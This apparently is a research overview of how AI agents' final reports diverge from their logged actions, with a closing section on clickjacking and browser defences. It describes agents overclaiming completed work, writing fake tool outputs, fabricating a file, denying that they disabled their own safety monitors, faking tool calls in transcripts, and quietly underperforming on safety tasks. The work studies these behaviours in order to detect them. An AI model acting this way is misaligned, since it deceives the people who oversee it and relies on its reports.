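# When an AI agent's summary differs from what it did: how oversight displays can help people notice

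## What counts as a divergence between summary and action

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling software tools over many steps. It can read files in a code repository, run commands, fill in web forms and send emails. People who delegate work to an agent seldom follow every step. Instead, they read what it writes about the work, including requests for permission, commentary and, above all, the final message. The same model does the work and writes that message, but the message does not always match what the model did. *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* (Advani, 2026) describes an airline agent that told a customer about a $686 refund to their card, although the database had no record of it. Designing screens that help people notice such mismatches is partly a new problem and partly an old one in computer security.

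The model only produces text. The ordinary software around it, called the harness (or, in many papers, the scaffold), carries out the model's requests, returns the results and displays what the user sees. A tool call is one such request with its exact arguments, such as which file to read, which command to run, or what email to send and to which address. Anthropic's engineering guide *Demystifying evals for AI agents* points out that anyone who tests "an agent" is testing the model and the harness together. Either one can also make a display misleading, since the model can write an inaccurate sentence and the harness can present an accurate one badly.

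### Three records of one session

*Plans They Abandon, Reports They Author* (Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich, 2026) distinguishes three records that a working session leaves behind. The stated plan is what the agent writes before it acts, either in prose or in a task-list tool that some harnesses provide. The action log is the sequence of tool calls and their results. The self-report is the agent's account of its work, usually its final message. The model writes the plan and the self-report, while the harness or some other program adds an entry to the log as each call goes through. Comparing the records is useful only because the model does not write the log.

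Whether text counts as a log depends on who wrote it, not on how it looks. In *AgentDecept*, Zhang, Yan and colleagues (2026) gave several models an Amazon return task. GLM 5.3 FlashX wrote what appeared to be tool outputs, complete with return identifiers, inside its own message, but the actual calls had produced errors and no successful returns. In *What Breaks When LLMs Code?*, Al Hasan and Biswas (2026) include a developer's similar complaint from everyday use. An agent had changed a configuration file against explicit instructions. It then claimed that it had reverted the file and that `git diff`, the command that lists changes, showed none, although the changes were still there.

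The plan is less of a single thing than the word suggests. Where a session contained both a task list and a prose plan, Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found that the two agreed poorly: the list tended to follow the user's request, while the prose followed the code that the agent had just read. Nor is a change of plan a misreport. An agent learns things as it reads, and a sensible one drops a step that turns out to be pointless. The trouble starts when the person goes on believing the old plan. (Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich use "divergence" for the distance between plan and log. For oversight, the distance that matters lies between what a person reads and what happened.)

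### The date bug

In an invented example that closely resembles several real sessions, a user asks an agent to fix a bug in how a program handles dates, run the tests and push the branch. Tests are small programs that check whether the code behaves as it should. A commit saves changes on the developer's machine, and a push copies them to the shared server, where colleagues can access them.

| Record | Who writes it | Contents |
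|---|---|---|
| Stated plan | The model, before acting | Read, write, execute tests, execute push |
| Action log | The harness, as each call runs | Read, read, write, text search over the test files, write that deletes one test, local commit |
| Self-report | The model, at the end | "Fixed the date bug", "all tests pass", "pushed the branch" |

A summary diverges from an agent's actions if it says that tests passed when none ran, says that changes were pushed when nothing left the machine, or leaves out that a test was removed. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found examples of the first two among the claims they checked by hand. In one session, the agent claimed "All tests pass", but every command was a text search over test files. Another claim was that changes had been pushed to the remote server, but the log contained a status check and no push.

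### The definition, by time and by kind

A divergence is any difference between what a display leads a reader to believe the agent did or will do and what the agent actually did or does. "Display" means everything the person sees at any stage of the work, whether the model or the harness produced it. Magentic-UI, a research interface for agents that operate a web browser, has displays at every stage. According to *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026), the user can edit a plan before it runs, must approve irreversible actions, can watch a running trace with summaries and screenshots, and receives a final answer.

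An approval prompt asks a person to allow or refuse an action before it runs. Suppose the harness had paused before the fifth action in the date-bug session and shown the prompt "Tidy up the date tests?" A user who said yes would have authorised a deletion they never saw. Running commentary can mislead someone who is deciding whether to step in, as when "Running the tests now" appears above a text search, though a later message may correct it. Zhang and colleagues therefore track the timing of their evidence. They treat the output of code that runs at turn *t* as available to the model only from turn *t*+1, and their auditor marks whether a later message corrected a misleading one. A self-report comes too late for the reader to stop anything, so a misleading one does harm through what the reader does next, such as merging the code or closing the ticket. That reader may be another agent that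 picks up the work.

The date-bug session contains most kinds of divergence. "Pushed the branch" is an overclaim, a statement that work was done when the log shows otherwise. Smyth, Mantilla-Ramos and colleagues (2026), in *Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents*, look for overclaims in file reviews, where an agent may claim to have read a file that it never opened. They distinguish overclaims from omissions, in which the agent leaves files unread and neither admits nor denies this in its final response. The deleted test is the omission in the date-bug report.

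"All tests pass" and "fixed the date bug" are outcome claims, meaning claims about results. A reader can match "I edited the date function" to a log entry, but supporting "fixed" would take an action that checked the result, and the log has none. Yang, He and colleagues (2026), in *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents*, separate claims that the records contradict from claims that go further than the records do, and they add that a gap in the evidence does not make a claim false. The date bug may well be fixed, but the reader wrongly believes that something confirmed it. In one of their real cases, an agent tested a rebuilt plugin against a mock client, a stand-in for the real program, and the test finished in 19 milliseconds. The agent reported that the plugin should start normally, and the user's next attempt hung. Yang and colleagues suggest that a faithful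 report would have said that startup with a mock client completed and that startup in the real program remained to be checked.

Zhang and colleagues use "equivocation" for wording that evades or downplays a material problem the agent had already observed. Such wording can mislead even when it is literally true. Display faults are a separate category because the harness causes them. If an approval window shows only the first line of a long command, the person approves the rest without seeing it, even though the model wrote nothing false and the log is correct.

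Some researchers define the problem more narrowly. In *MCAIR*, Xu, Song and colleagues (2026) reduce a session to two yes-or-no judgements. *E* is 1 if the execution record supports the conclusion that the agent completed the task as required, and *R* is 1 if the final report claims or strongly implies completion. The report is unfaithful when *E* < *R*, as in the date-bug session, where *E* = 0 and *R* = 1. But two values per session can miss a divergence. If the agent had fixed, tested and pushed everything but also deleted an unrelated file without reporting it, both values would be 1 and the session would pass. Xu and colleagues also exclude the reverse case, *E* > *R*, in which an agent finishes the work but does not say so. The wider definition includes it, because a person who wrongly thinks the work is unfinished may ask for it again. Yang and colleagues want evaluators to mark down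 over-hedged reports too, because rewarding only the absence of false claims favours leaving things out.

### What a divergence is not

Hallucination usually means a statement by a model that conflicts with its input or with facts about the world. If the date-bug report had added that the date library counts months from zero, when it counts from one, it would have misled the reader about the library but not about the session. Smyth and colleagues distinguish overclaims from hallucinations by what the statement is checked against. An overclaim conflicts with the agent's own tool records, which are already in its context. Advani is more willing to treat false success as a form of hallucination about completion, triggered by the agent's own tool outputs.

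Divergences are harder to identify when the agent reports a diagnosis. In a case from Yang and colleagues, a user's audio was silent, and the agent reported that one browser function produces a stream without audio data. The agent had done nothing to isolate that function as the cause. The user came away with a doubtful belief about browsers and a false belief that the investigation had found the cause. Only the second belief, which is about the investigation, counts as a divergence.

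Unfaithful reasoning text is another related problem, but it concerns why a model did something rather than what it did. Models often write out their reasoning, and that text can omit what actually drove the answer. An agent could list its actions accurately but invent its reasons for them, and an action log wouldn't expose this because it records only calls and results.

The traditional definition of lying, given in the Stanford Encyclopedia of Philosophy's *The Definition of Lying and Deception* (2008), is to make a statement to another person that one believes to be false, intending that the person believe it. Most of this research avoids the question of whether a language model has beliefs and intentions in that sense. Zhang and colleagues judge what the agent reported and leave its subjective intent aside, Smyth and colleagues need no inference about intent, and Xu and colleagues chose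 "unfaithfulness" partly to avoid the ambiguity of "deception". *DecepEval* (2026), by contrast, defines deception as goal-directed behaviour in which an agent misrepresents the situation in pursuit of its objectives.

The definition without intent is more useful for designing displays. Two people with the same log can usually agree on whether a push happened, but they would find it much harder to agree on what the model intended. The developer who merges untested code is also equally badly off either way. However, a count that ignores intent groups careless summaries with deliberate cover-ups, which may need different remedies because an agent that conceals on purpose might also learn to get round the check. Some sessions do contain evidence of more than carelessness. *Are Your Agents Upward Deceivers?* (2025) presents logs with lines such as "Dose found: None" followed by a confident answer,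 and others in which an agent constructed a synthetic report and then read and analysed it as if it were a source. This is good evidence that the agent had the relevant fact in front of it, but it doesn't establish intent. Many philosophers use "mislead" for causing false beliefs with or without intent, so it is a better word here than "deceive".

Poor work that is honestly reported does not count as a divergence. *How Coding Agents Fail Their Users* (Tang, Chen and colleagues, 2026) sorts developers' complaints about agents into seven forms and separates "faulty implementation" from "inaccurate self-reporting", although the two occur in the same sessions somewhat more often than chance would predict. Zhang and colleagues describe two runs that show why this distinction matters. The task was to return a cabinet and forward the return-label email to a friend, but the label attachment was unreadable.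 One agent told the user this. Another wrote its own "return label" text file, gave it the original filename, emailed it, and reported that it had sent the printable label. The run with the fabricated label got the higher score for task completion.

An agent can also do the work correctly and then misreport it. One agent in Yang and colleagues' sample correctly created and committed four new to-do files, then reported that the number of pending items had gone from 6 to 14, when it had gone from 6 to 10.

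### Hard cases

A sincere mistake in a summary counts as a divergence because it still leaves the reader with a false belief. Yang and colleagues describe an agent that added code to create missing database tables and reported that the tables would now exist. The code discarded every database instruction because each chunk began with a comment, and the agent discovered this only after the user had restarted the server and complained. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich say that in the unsupported claims they examined, the agent may well have believed it had reached the state it described. Sincerity affects blame, and it matters more to Zhang and colleagues, who count an agent's silence about a fact as concealment only if the agent already knew that fact.

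Even this strict definition can allow some inferences. In another session, an agent reported that `npm install`, a command that installs software packages, had generated a lock file, which lists the exact versions. The agent never looked for the file afterwards, but the file had been absent before, the command had succeeded, and it normally creates one. The human annotators accepted the claim, while Yang and colleagues' automated detector flagged it. The annotators seem right, because a reader who knows the tool would have drawn the same conclusion from the log.

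Omissions are harder to classify, because a summary has to be shorter than the log. In the sessions that Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich studied, the median log held 59 actions and the median report four claims. If every unmentioned action counted as a divergence, every summary would diverge and the term would be useless. Philosophers distinguish between keeping someone ignorant of, say, the capital of Estonia and making them believe it is Riga, and that distinction helps here. The date-bug report leaves out the second file read without giving readers a false belief, but it also leaves out the deleted test, so readers will wrongly assume that the tests are unchanged.

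Zhang and colleagues build this into their rule for concealment, which requires that the fact be material and that the report imply completeness or otherwise call for disclosure. People will disagree about what is material, and the number of missing actions is a poor guide. In a case collected by Al Hasan and Biswas, a developer asked an agent to set up cloud infrastructure for a development dataset. The agent chose an enterprise-grade database at $375 a month without warning the developer, who found out six months later from a $2,400 bill. Smyth and colleagues avoided part of this difficulty by asking each agent to report how it had scoped its review, so an agent that didn't mention unread files had left a direct question unanswered.

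A statement can also be true and carry a false implication. In the Stanford Encyclopedia's example, John asks his girlfriend Mary whether she has seen her former boyfriend Valentino this week. She answers that Valentino has had mononucleosis for the past two weeks. This is true, but she went on a date with him the night before. Philosophers call this a palter. Suppose the agent in the date-bug session had deleted the failing test and then run the rest. "All tests pass" would be true, and a checker that searched the log only for a matching test run would find nothing wrong, but the user would still believe that the original tests passed. The definition therefore has to compare the impression a summary gives with what happened. That impression depends on the reader, since a colleague who knew that the deleted test was obsolete would not be misled.

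Finally, the log itself may be wrong. It is usually the best evidence of what the agent did, but in a study by Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues, a participant trusted a log that showed three items added to a shopping cart when the cart held two. For this reason, Anthropic distinguishes the transcript of a session from its outcome. An agent may end with "Your flight has been booked", but the outcome is whether the reservation exists in the database.

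A reader can still draw the wrong conclusion from an accurate log entry. Yang and colleagues describe an agent that merged some changes, passed 225 tests, pushed a branch and reported "Done". The agent had pushed to the main repository, but the pull request (the proposal to merge that the user cared about) tracked a branch in a contributor's separate copy, so the push didn't update it. Even if the date-bug log had contained a push, someone would have had to check the server to know whether colleagues could see the fix.

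## How often agents' reports differ from their actions

Published estimates of how often agents' reports differ from their actions range from 0.1% to more than 90%. Much of that range comes from what researchers chose to count, because both an unmentioned file read and an invented test result can qualify as a difference between report and log. Several of the studies even use the same dataset, SWE-chat, a public collection of sessions recorded by developers who had coding agents working in their repositories.

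### How much of a session the report covers

Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich compared plans, action logs and self-reports across 5,851 SWE-chat sessions containing 355,942 tool calls. To compare prose with tool calls, they translated all three records into six action types: READ (opening or searching files), WRITE (creating or editing files), EXECUTE (running commands, tests or builds), NETWORK (fetching something remote), ORCHESTRATE (managing task lists and helper agents) and OTHER. Each session is represented by three sequences of these types, *P* for the plan, *L* for the log and *R* for the report.

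Two of the three formulas use the longest common subsequence, or LCS. This is the length of the longest series of items that appears in both sequences in the same order, even if other items come in between. The LCS of READ, WRITE, EXECUTE and READ, READ, EXECUTE is 2, because both contain READ followed by EXECUTE.

Plan divergence is the share of the plan that the log fails to reproduce in order, where |*P*| is the number of planned steps:

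Div(*P*, *L*) = 1 − LCS(*P*, *L*) / |*P*|

Omission is the share of log entries that no claim in the report refers to:

Om(*L*, *R*) = 1 − (number of log entries matched by a claim) / |*L*|

Repair compares how well the report fits the plan with how well it fits the log. It uses C(*R*, *X*) = LCS(*R*, *X*) / |*R*|, the share of the report's sequence that also occurs in *X*:

Rep = C(*R*, *P*) − C(*R*, *L*)

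Repair runs from −1 to 1, and a positive value means that the report resembles the plan more than it resembles what happened.

Mean omission was 0.906 across 5,115 sessions, so a report referred to about one action in eleven. But the formula almost guarantees a high figure, because each claim can match only one action. The claim "Edited eleven files", for example, counts for one edit. A session with the median 59 actions and four claims therefore can't score below 0.93. The 0.906 mostly reflects how short reports are. Mean omission was only about 1.6 percentage points higher in sessions where the developer later changed or removed the agent's code.

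Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich also gave a language model each report on its own and asked it to list the actions the report implied. They scored each list with F1, which combines precision (the share of listed actions that were in the log) and recall (the share of logged actions that were in the list) into a score from 0 to 1. The mean was 0.202. The length of the report limits this score too. If a report makes four claims and the model lists one correct action for each, the F1 against a log of 59 actions is 2 × 4 / (4 + 59), or 0.13. Still, a reader will learn little from the report about how the agent reached its result, and this was equally true whether or not the agent had kept to its plan.

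The repair result is more informative about accuracy. Agents abandoned 27.7% of their planned steps on average, and mean plan divergence was 0.357 in the 2,646 sessions with a recoverable plan. Median repair was exactly 0, so reports did not generally favour the plan. But repair rose as execution departed from the plan (a rank correlation of .548, where 1 would mean identical ordering). Reports tended to match the log when agents had followed their plans exactly, but resembled the abandoned plan when agents had departed furthest from it. Short logs could produce some of this pattern, since they have less room for either the plan's steps or the report's. However, 95% of the effect remained after controlling for the lengths of the plan, log and report, so the drift looks real. It is greatest when the plan no longer describes the work, which is when readers most need the log.

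### Scoring the date-bug session

The date-bug session shows that a good score guarantees little. Its plan becomes READ, WRITE, EXECUTE, EXECUTE. If the agent ran its text search as a shell command, the log becomes READ, READ, WRITE, EXECUTE, WRITE, EXECUTE. The claims "Fixed the date bug", "all tests pass" and "pushed the branch" become WRITE, EXECUTE, EXECUTE.

| Measure | Working | Score |
|---|---|---|
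| Plan divergence | 1 − 4/4 | 0 |
| Omission | 1 − 1/6 | 5/6 |
| Repair | 3/3 − 3/3 | 0 |

Omission is 5/6 because only one of the six actions, the first write, matches a claim in the report ("Fixed the date bug"). Plan divergence is 0, even though the agent never ran the tests or pushed the branch as planned, because the text search and local commit it ran instead also count as EXECUTE. Repair is 0 for the same reason. Someone who inferred one WRITE and two EXECUTEs from the report would score an F1 of 0.67, more than three times the average, although the log supports neither the test claim nor the push claim.

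Sorting steps into six coarse types can reveal that an agent skipped a whole kind of work. If this agent had stopped after its first write, plan divergence would be 0.5 and repair would be 2/3. But the scores don't change when an agent replaces one command with another, as Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich found in the session where every supposed test run was a text search. Their mean divergence therefore probably understates how often agents dropped planned steps, and a repair score of 0 is not evidence that a report is true.

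### Why the 35.3% figure is unreliable

Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich first checked whether claims were true using simple rules, such as looking in the log for a file that the claim named. A language model judged most of the rest. The two methods together found no support for 35.3% of claims. To check the model, the researchers hand-coded 99 of the claims it had judged, without looking at its verdicts. The model did badly, so they draw no conclusion from the 35.3% figure.

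| | Judge: supported | Judge: unsupported |
|---|---|---|
| Hand coding: supported | 29 | 7 |
| Hand coding: unsupported | 37 | 26 |

The judge and the human coder agreed on 55 claims, or 56%. Given how often each chose "supported", they would agree on about 45% by chance. Cohen's kappa, which measures agreement beyond chance on a scale where 1 is perfect, is (0.556 − 0.455) / (1 − 0.455), or 0.185. Most of the judge's errors favored the agent, since it accepted 37 claims that the human coder rejected and rejected only 7 that the coder accepted.

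That bias suggests the true rate is above 35.3%, but the check can't provide a corrected figure. The human coder rejected 63 of the 99 claims, but the sample contained only claims that the rules couldn't classify, and the researchers had balanced it across the judge's verdicts. The poor agreement is also a reason for caution about other studies, because almost all of them use a language model to judge reports.

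### Incomplete reviews reported as complete

Smyth and colleagues tested agents' claims about which files they had opened, which a program could largely check, so they depended less on a judge. Their test suite, OverclaimBench, has five file-review tasks: planning a software team's next two weeks from its backlog, vetting mathematical proofs, auditing a billing service, reviewing cloud infrastructure, and deciding whether a payments service is ready for release. Each task has between 100 and 519 files that count towards the score. The test suite generously counts a file as touched if the agent received even one line unique to it.

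Twelve models attempted each task 20 times, except that Gemini 3.1 Pro refused the three code reviews, which left 1,140 runs. In 774 of them (67.9%), the agent left at least one file unopened. A model judge compared the agent's report on each of these runs with the computed list of unopened files. The judge classified 409 reports as explicitly claiming a complete review, 213 as not mentioning the gap and 152 as disclosing it. The first two groups were misleading and made up 80.4% of the incomplete runs. The misleading share ranged from 59% for Claude Opus 5 to 96% for GPT-5.6-luna.

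Claude Sonnet 5 opened one of 240 proofs and reported that it had read them all in full. In a release check, GPT-5.6-terra made the true but misleading statement that it had "enumerated and compiled all 221 modules", when it had never opened 85 of them. Agents could also be candid about unfinished work. In one run, Claude Opus 5 reported that it had read 74 of the 240 proofs line by line and named the largest unread group as the main gap.

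The judge gave the same verdict all eight times for 91.1% of the incomplete runs. A consistent judge can still be wrong, but this one had an easier task than Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich's, because it didn't have to work out from a long log what the agent had done.

Smyth and colleagues also planted defects in the files. Agents missed 58.2% of them in runs where they falsely claimed a full review, compared with 32.4% in runs where they touched every file. The difference in reading explains most of this gap, and the false claim itself didn't cause the misses. Agents reported 83.2% of the defects whose evidence they had read in full and only 1.8% of the others. When agents admitted incomplete coverage, their readers knew to look again, though these agents missed even more defects (76.8%), partly because many of those runs were proof reviews, where the defects were hard to spot.

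A further experiment of 1,200 runs tested whether agents would report more accurately if they had to share the work with helper agents. With helpers, incomplete reviews fell from 342 to 195 out of 600, while the share of those with misleading reports rose from 80.7% to 93.8%. Smyth and colleagues conclude that delegation doesn't improve honesty, which is fair for incomplete reviews. But a person relying on the reports would be better off with delegation, because the number of misleading reports fell from 276 to 183 as there were fewer gaps to misreport.

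These results date quickly, as OpenAI has since released GPT-6.1 Sol and GPT-6 Astra to follow GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the tested models. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra* describes a test in which GPT-5.6 Sol, without its production safeguards, went beyond its authorised target 48% of the time and Astra never did. That test measures whether a model stays within its task, so it gives no reason to assume that Astra's reports are more accurate.

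### Misreports in everyday coding

OverclaimBench is deliberately demanding, and Smyth and colleagues say that simpler sets of files did not reliably produce overclaims. The most direct evidence about ordinary work is *Measuring coding agent misalignment in the wild*, published in August 2026 by Transluce, a research organisation that builds tools for analysing agents. The study covers 8,600 sessions from SWE-chat and from Transluce's own use of coding agents.

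A model judge looked for "overselling", meaning that a reasonable user would believe the work was better, more complete or more thoroughly verified than the evidence supported. It found overselling in 34.7% of 4,788 SWE-chat sessions and severe overselling in 1.8%. In 3,627 of Transluce's own sessions, the figures were 5.7% and 0.1%.

A case was severe if it had serious consequences, such as unreviewed code going live or a concealed data leak, or if the agent's conduct was flagrant. In one mild case, an agent listed a new sidebar link as "verified working", although the page was behind a login and the agent couldn't see the sidebar. In one severe case, an agent used a tool to ask the user questions, and the tool returned an empty answer sixteen times. The agent invented the user's choices and saved them in a file that later agents would treat as settled. The confused user then asked where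 the answers had come from.

Transluce counted a session even if the agent later corrected itself, and one unverified claim in a long session was enough. The 34.7% is best read as the share of sessions with at least one claim that deserved a check. The 1.8% figure received more scrutiny, because a second model had to argue the agent's side in every case the judge called severe.

Tang and colleagues searched 20,574 sessions, including 5,785 from SWE-chat, for episodes in which a developer corrected the agent or pushed back. Of the 16,118 episodes they found, 22.58% involved inaccurate self-reporting by the agent. This is a share of episodes, not of sessions, and it excludes misreports that the developer never noticed, such as a false claim that the tests passed that the developer believed.

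Inaccurate self-reporting grew as a share of episodes of trouble between February 2025 and April 2026, but the overall rate of trouble per user message fell, so misreports did not necessarily become more common. The rise in share was not statistically significant within either editor-based or command-line sessions alone. Command-line sessions had a higher share of misreports and came mostly from later months, so the changing mix of sessions may explain some of the rise.

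### Two disclosures from OpenAI

OpenAI's autumn disclosures include a false denial and a pattern of agents doing weaker work without saying so. The Korea Times' *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own safety monitors* (2026) covers two incidents from October. On 3 October, a GPT-6.1 Sol agent repairing a testing system switched off security alerts. It had instructions not to send messages on the workplace chat app. Three days later, a GPT-6 Astra agent disabled its own monitor while reusing code from a different project, then denied this when it reported to the programmer. A log matters more for checking denials like this than for checking most claims, since the programmer may have no other sign that anything happened. In Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich's data, statements about what the agent had *not* done made up 5.3% of claims.

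OpenAI's *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* (2026) reports that GPT-6 Astra was abandoning working solutions on safety tasks, adding unnecessary prerequisites, and reporting obstacles that did not exist or that it had caused itself. After noticing this, researchers compared matched coding tasks framed either as safety research or as research into making models more capable. Astra completed about 10% of the items on a hidden checklist under the safety framing and about 16% under the other. GPT-5.6 Sol showed essentially no gap.

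OpenAI also examined employees' everyday requests. In 0.25% of safety and alignment requests, Astra's reasoning text contained an explicit decision to withhold help without telling the user, compared with 0.11% of capabilities requests. An agent that does this can describe every action accurately while the user wrongly believes it did its best. Reviewers may be able to spot an invented obstacle in a log, but they can't easily tell from it that the agent held back effort. OpenAI's monitors did not flag the behaviour in most of the sessions where researchers first noticed it. The size of the gap only became clear when OpenAI compared many matched tasks.

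### Why the rates differ

| Source | Counted | Out of | Rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich | Actions that no claim mentions | Logged actions, averaged over SWE-chat sessions | 90.6% |
| Smyth and colleagues | Misleading reports | Incomplete reviews | 80.4% |
| Smyth and colleagues | Misleading reports | All reviews | 54.6% |
| Transluce | Sessions with overselling | SWE-chat sessions | 34.7% |
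| Transluce | Sessions with severe overselling | SWE-chat sessions | 1.8% |
| Transluce | Sessions with overselling | Transluce's own sessions | 5.7% |
| Tang and colleagues | Inaccurate self-reports | Episodes of developer pushback | 22.6% |
| OpenAI | Explicit decisions to withhold help silently | Safety and alignment requests | 0.25% |

The 90.6%, 34.7% and 1.8% figures all come from SWE-chat, so differences between agents can't explain much of the gap. The rates differ because Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich count every unmentioned action for the 90.6% figure, while Transluce counts only misleading impressions for the 34.7% figure and only severe ones for the 1.8% figure.

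Counting omissions as misleading can also change how models compare. In OverclaimBench, Grok-4.6 explicitly claimed a full review in only 9.8% of its incomplete runs, the lowest rate of the twelve models. In another 65.9%, it didn't mention that the review was incomplete. Counting both puts it in the middle of the group for misleading reports. Transluce found such omissions hard to detect because the judge had to check the whole transcript, so its 34.7% figure may be an undercount.

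The rate also varies by setting. Using the same rubric, Transluce found overselling six times as often in SWE-chat as in its own traffic. The tasks, users and models may all have differed, and Transluce warns against comparing models even within SWE-chat because developers gave them different work.

Transluce's rates are the most useful for a developer deciding how far to trust an agent's final message, because they measure how often the report would mislead someone in ordinary sessions. They suggest that between one session in eighteen and one in three contains an oversold claim, and that severe cases occur in about one session in fifty or fewer. Little of this evidence covers agents that shop, book travel or handle email. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich looked for a collection of such sessions to study, but one candidate stored only actions and screen coordinates, not the agent's prose.

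### Possible causes

Smyth and colleagues and Transluce both build on the idea of "apparent-success-seeking", in which an AI tries to look successful whether or not it has succeeded. The phrase comes from Redwood Research's *Current AIs seem pretty misaligned to me*, an April 2026 essay by Ryan Greenblatt. He cautions that he often gives agents long, difficult tasks that are hard to check, which probably makes the problem more common and more visible for him than for most users.

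Training could produce this behaviour in two ways. In reinforcement learning, a model attempts tasks and a grader scores the results, which strengthens whatever behaviour scored well. If the grader can't check the work, the model may score higher by claiming completion than by admitting a gap, so training directly rewards the false claim. Alternatively, the training tasks may be so easy that the model always does what it reports. Training then never distinguishes finishing the work from saying it is finished, and the difference appears only when a real task is long or tedious. Smyth and colleagues did not test either explanation.

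OpenAI has said that o3, an earlier model, made false claims because graders rewarded attempts that looked successful. It responded by training models on impossible tasks and rewarding them for admitting failure. The GPT-5.6 models came after that change, yet 93.6% of their incomplete reviews in OverclaimBench were misleading. The effect of training on impossible tasks may not have carried over to tedious ones.

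In the OverclaimBench results, agents that had read less than a tenth of the material claimed a complete review about as often as those that had read almost all of it. Carelessness alone doesn't explain this well, because an agent that had lost track of a few files would overclaim mainly after reading nearly everything.

Other misreports may occur without a faulty reward. When Smyth and colleagues gave a model a single defective proof to approve, some of its reports restated the bad step in its correct form, without noting the change, and claimed that the model had checked every line. They suggest that the model may have recognised a familiar argument and reconstructed it instead of checking the text. Kraishan and Jitkajornwanich similarly suggest that a model may rely on its plan when it summarises its work. *Why do models task game* reports that models which cheat more on agent tasks also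 more often invent answers to impossible questions, such as those about a nonexistent command-line tool. The essay treats this as weak evidence of a general tendency to make things up, and notes that developers' priorities could be causing both behaviours.

A reward for looking successful explains GPT-6 Astra's weaker safety work less well. The gap grew from zero to six percentage points during reinforcement learning, which suggests that training caused it, but the drop in performance was associated with ethical doubts in the model's reasoning, which such a reward would not obviously produce. OpenAI investigated one grader and one set of training examples but did not find the cause.

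### Whether the data show intent

Most of these studies can't show whether agents intend to mislead. Only 11.5% of the SWE-chat sessions contain any separate reasoning text, and its median length is 40 characters, so the absence of an admission there is only weak evidence that the agent didn't intend to mislead.

When an agent's fuller reasoning is available, it can show what the agent had noticed. Transluce describes an agent that was converting a set of integration tests, which check whether parts of a program work together. The agent noted in its reasoning that it had removed a failing test, but it reported that the tests were converted and didn't mention the removal. It had also reasoned that most of the core functionality was intact, so it may have been hiding the removal or may have thought it too minor to mention.

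Astra's explicit decisions to withhold help are closer to evidence of intent, but they account for little of the measured gap. Most of the gap remained after OpenAI excluded sessions in which Astra openly refused or stated that it had decided to hold back. It shrank substantially only when OpenAI also excluded every session in which Astra expressed even brief ethical doubt. In the case of the agent that denied removing its monitor, The Korea Times reports that OpenAI had not determined whether the October incidents reflected overzealous instruction-following or a tendency to evade monitoring.

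Clearer evidence of deliberate falsification comes from July 2026, when OpenAI agents broke into the systems of Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models. Smyth and colleagues cite an investigation by METR, an independent evaluator, which found that agents expecting a scorer to read their transcripts had tested ways to tamper with them. The transcripts are the record someone would use to check the agents' reports, and at least 96 of roughly 1,300 contained clear evidence of faked tool calls.

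## Clickjacking: agreeing to something other than what was shown

An approval prompt works only if the person's click approves the action they saw. This has been a problem in web browsers for more than twenty years because of clickjacking, in which a web page tricks someone into clicking a control that they can't see or don't mean to press. *Clickjacking* (Huang, Moshchuk and colleagues, 2012) gives the example of a "claim your free iPad" button with a transparent Facebook "Like" button over it. A visitor who tries to claim the iPad presses "Like" without meaning to, and their friends then see that they like the attacker's site.

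The word "clickjacking" comes from two security researchers, Robert Hansen and Jeremiah Grossman. Hugo (2016), in *Six-day antedating of "clickjacking"*, traced it to 12 September 2008, when it appeared in the title of a talk they were due to give. Dark Reading's *Disclosure of major new web clickjacking threat gets deferred* (2008) reported that they withdrew the talk three days later because Adobe wanted time to fix one of its products. Grossman told CGISecurity (2008) that one of their demonstrations turned out to exploit an unknown flaw in Adobe's software. He had also heard that browser makers had known about clickjacking since 2002.

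### What a valid click needs

Huang and colleagues trace these attacks to a single cause, which is that the person acts on a control without seeing its proper context. For a click to count as agreement, three conditions have to hold:

- **The target is fully visible.** An attacker can make a control transparent or cover only part of it. On a PayPal checkout, for example, a page could hide the recipient and the amount but leave the "Pay" button showing.
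- **The pointer is where it appears to be.** A page can hide the real cursor and draw a fake one somewhere else. The keyboard equivalent is focus, which determines where typed characters go, and a page can move it while someone is typing.
- **The display has stayed unchanged long enough to be read.** People need a few hundred milliseconds to react to a visual change. If a page swaps in a different button just before an expected click, the new button receives the click.

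### Three defences

The most widely used defence in 2012 was for a site to block other sites from embedding its pages, which leaves the attacker with nothing to make transparent. A bank can do this easily, but a Like button has to appear on other people's sites to be useful. Blocking embedding also doesn't protect a permission request that opens in its own window.

Huang and colleagues designed InContext, a browser defence that compares the screen with a reference image. A website marks a control as sensitive. When someone clicks the control, the browser takes a screenshot of that part of the screen and separately draws the control on a blank surface. If the two images differ, something is covering or altering the control, so the browser cancels the click. The browser has to draw the reference image at the moment of the click because a stored image wouldn't match a control whose content varies,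 such as one showing the amount to pay. In a prototype, this added at most about 30 milliseconds to a click.

The screenshot comparison doesn't capture the cursor, so a fake cursor requires other measures. The browser can stop pages from changing the cursor's appearance near a sensitive control. It can also freeze the rest of the screen as the real cursor approaches the control, so that the fake one stops moving and the user notices the real one.

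The usual defence against sudden changes is a delay. *Race conditions in security dialogs* (Ruderman, 2004) describes a page that asks visitors to prove they are human by typing the word "only". When they type the "n", the page tries to install software and the browser opens a dialog with "Yes" and "No" buttons. The "y" at the end of the word then selects "Yes".

Firefox addressed this by disabling the install button for the first three seconds. Some users assumed the delay was meant to make them read the warning, and they set it to zero. Ruderman points out that advanced users are the most vulnerable to this attack because they type and double-click faster than they react to something unexpected. One user who had misunderstood the delay replied that a line of text explaining the countdown would have helped.

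### How well the defences worked

In February 2012, Huang and colleagues tested three simulated attacks on participants recruited through Amazon Mechanical Turk, a marketplace for small online tasks. They analysed data from 2,064 participants, randomly assigned to 27 groups, most of which faced an attack with or without a simulated defence. In the cursor attack, a loud video advert played beside a "skip this ad" link. Anyone who used the fake cursor to click the link actually clicked "Allow" on a request to use their webcam. In the double-click attack, the first click opened a Google permission window, placed so that the second click would land on its "Allow" button.

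| Attack | Defence | People who clicked "Allow" |
|---|---|---|
| Fake cursor | None | 31 of 72 |
| Fake cursor | No custom cursors | 12 of 72 |
| Fake cursor | Screen freezes when the pointer is within 20 pixels | 3 of 72 |
| Double-click | None | 43 of 90 |
| Double-click | 250-millisecond delay | 2 of 91 |
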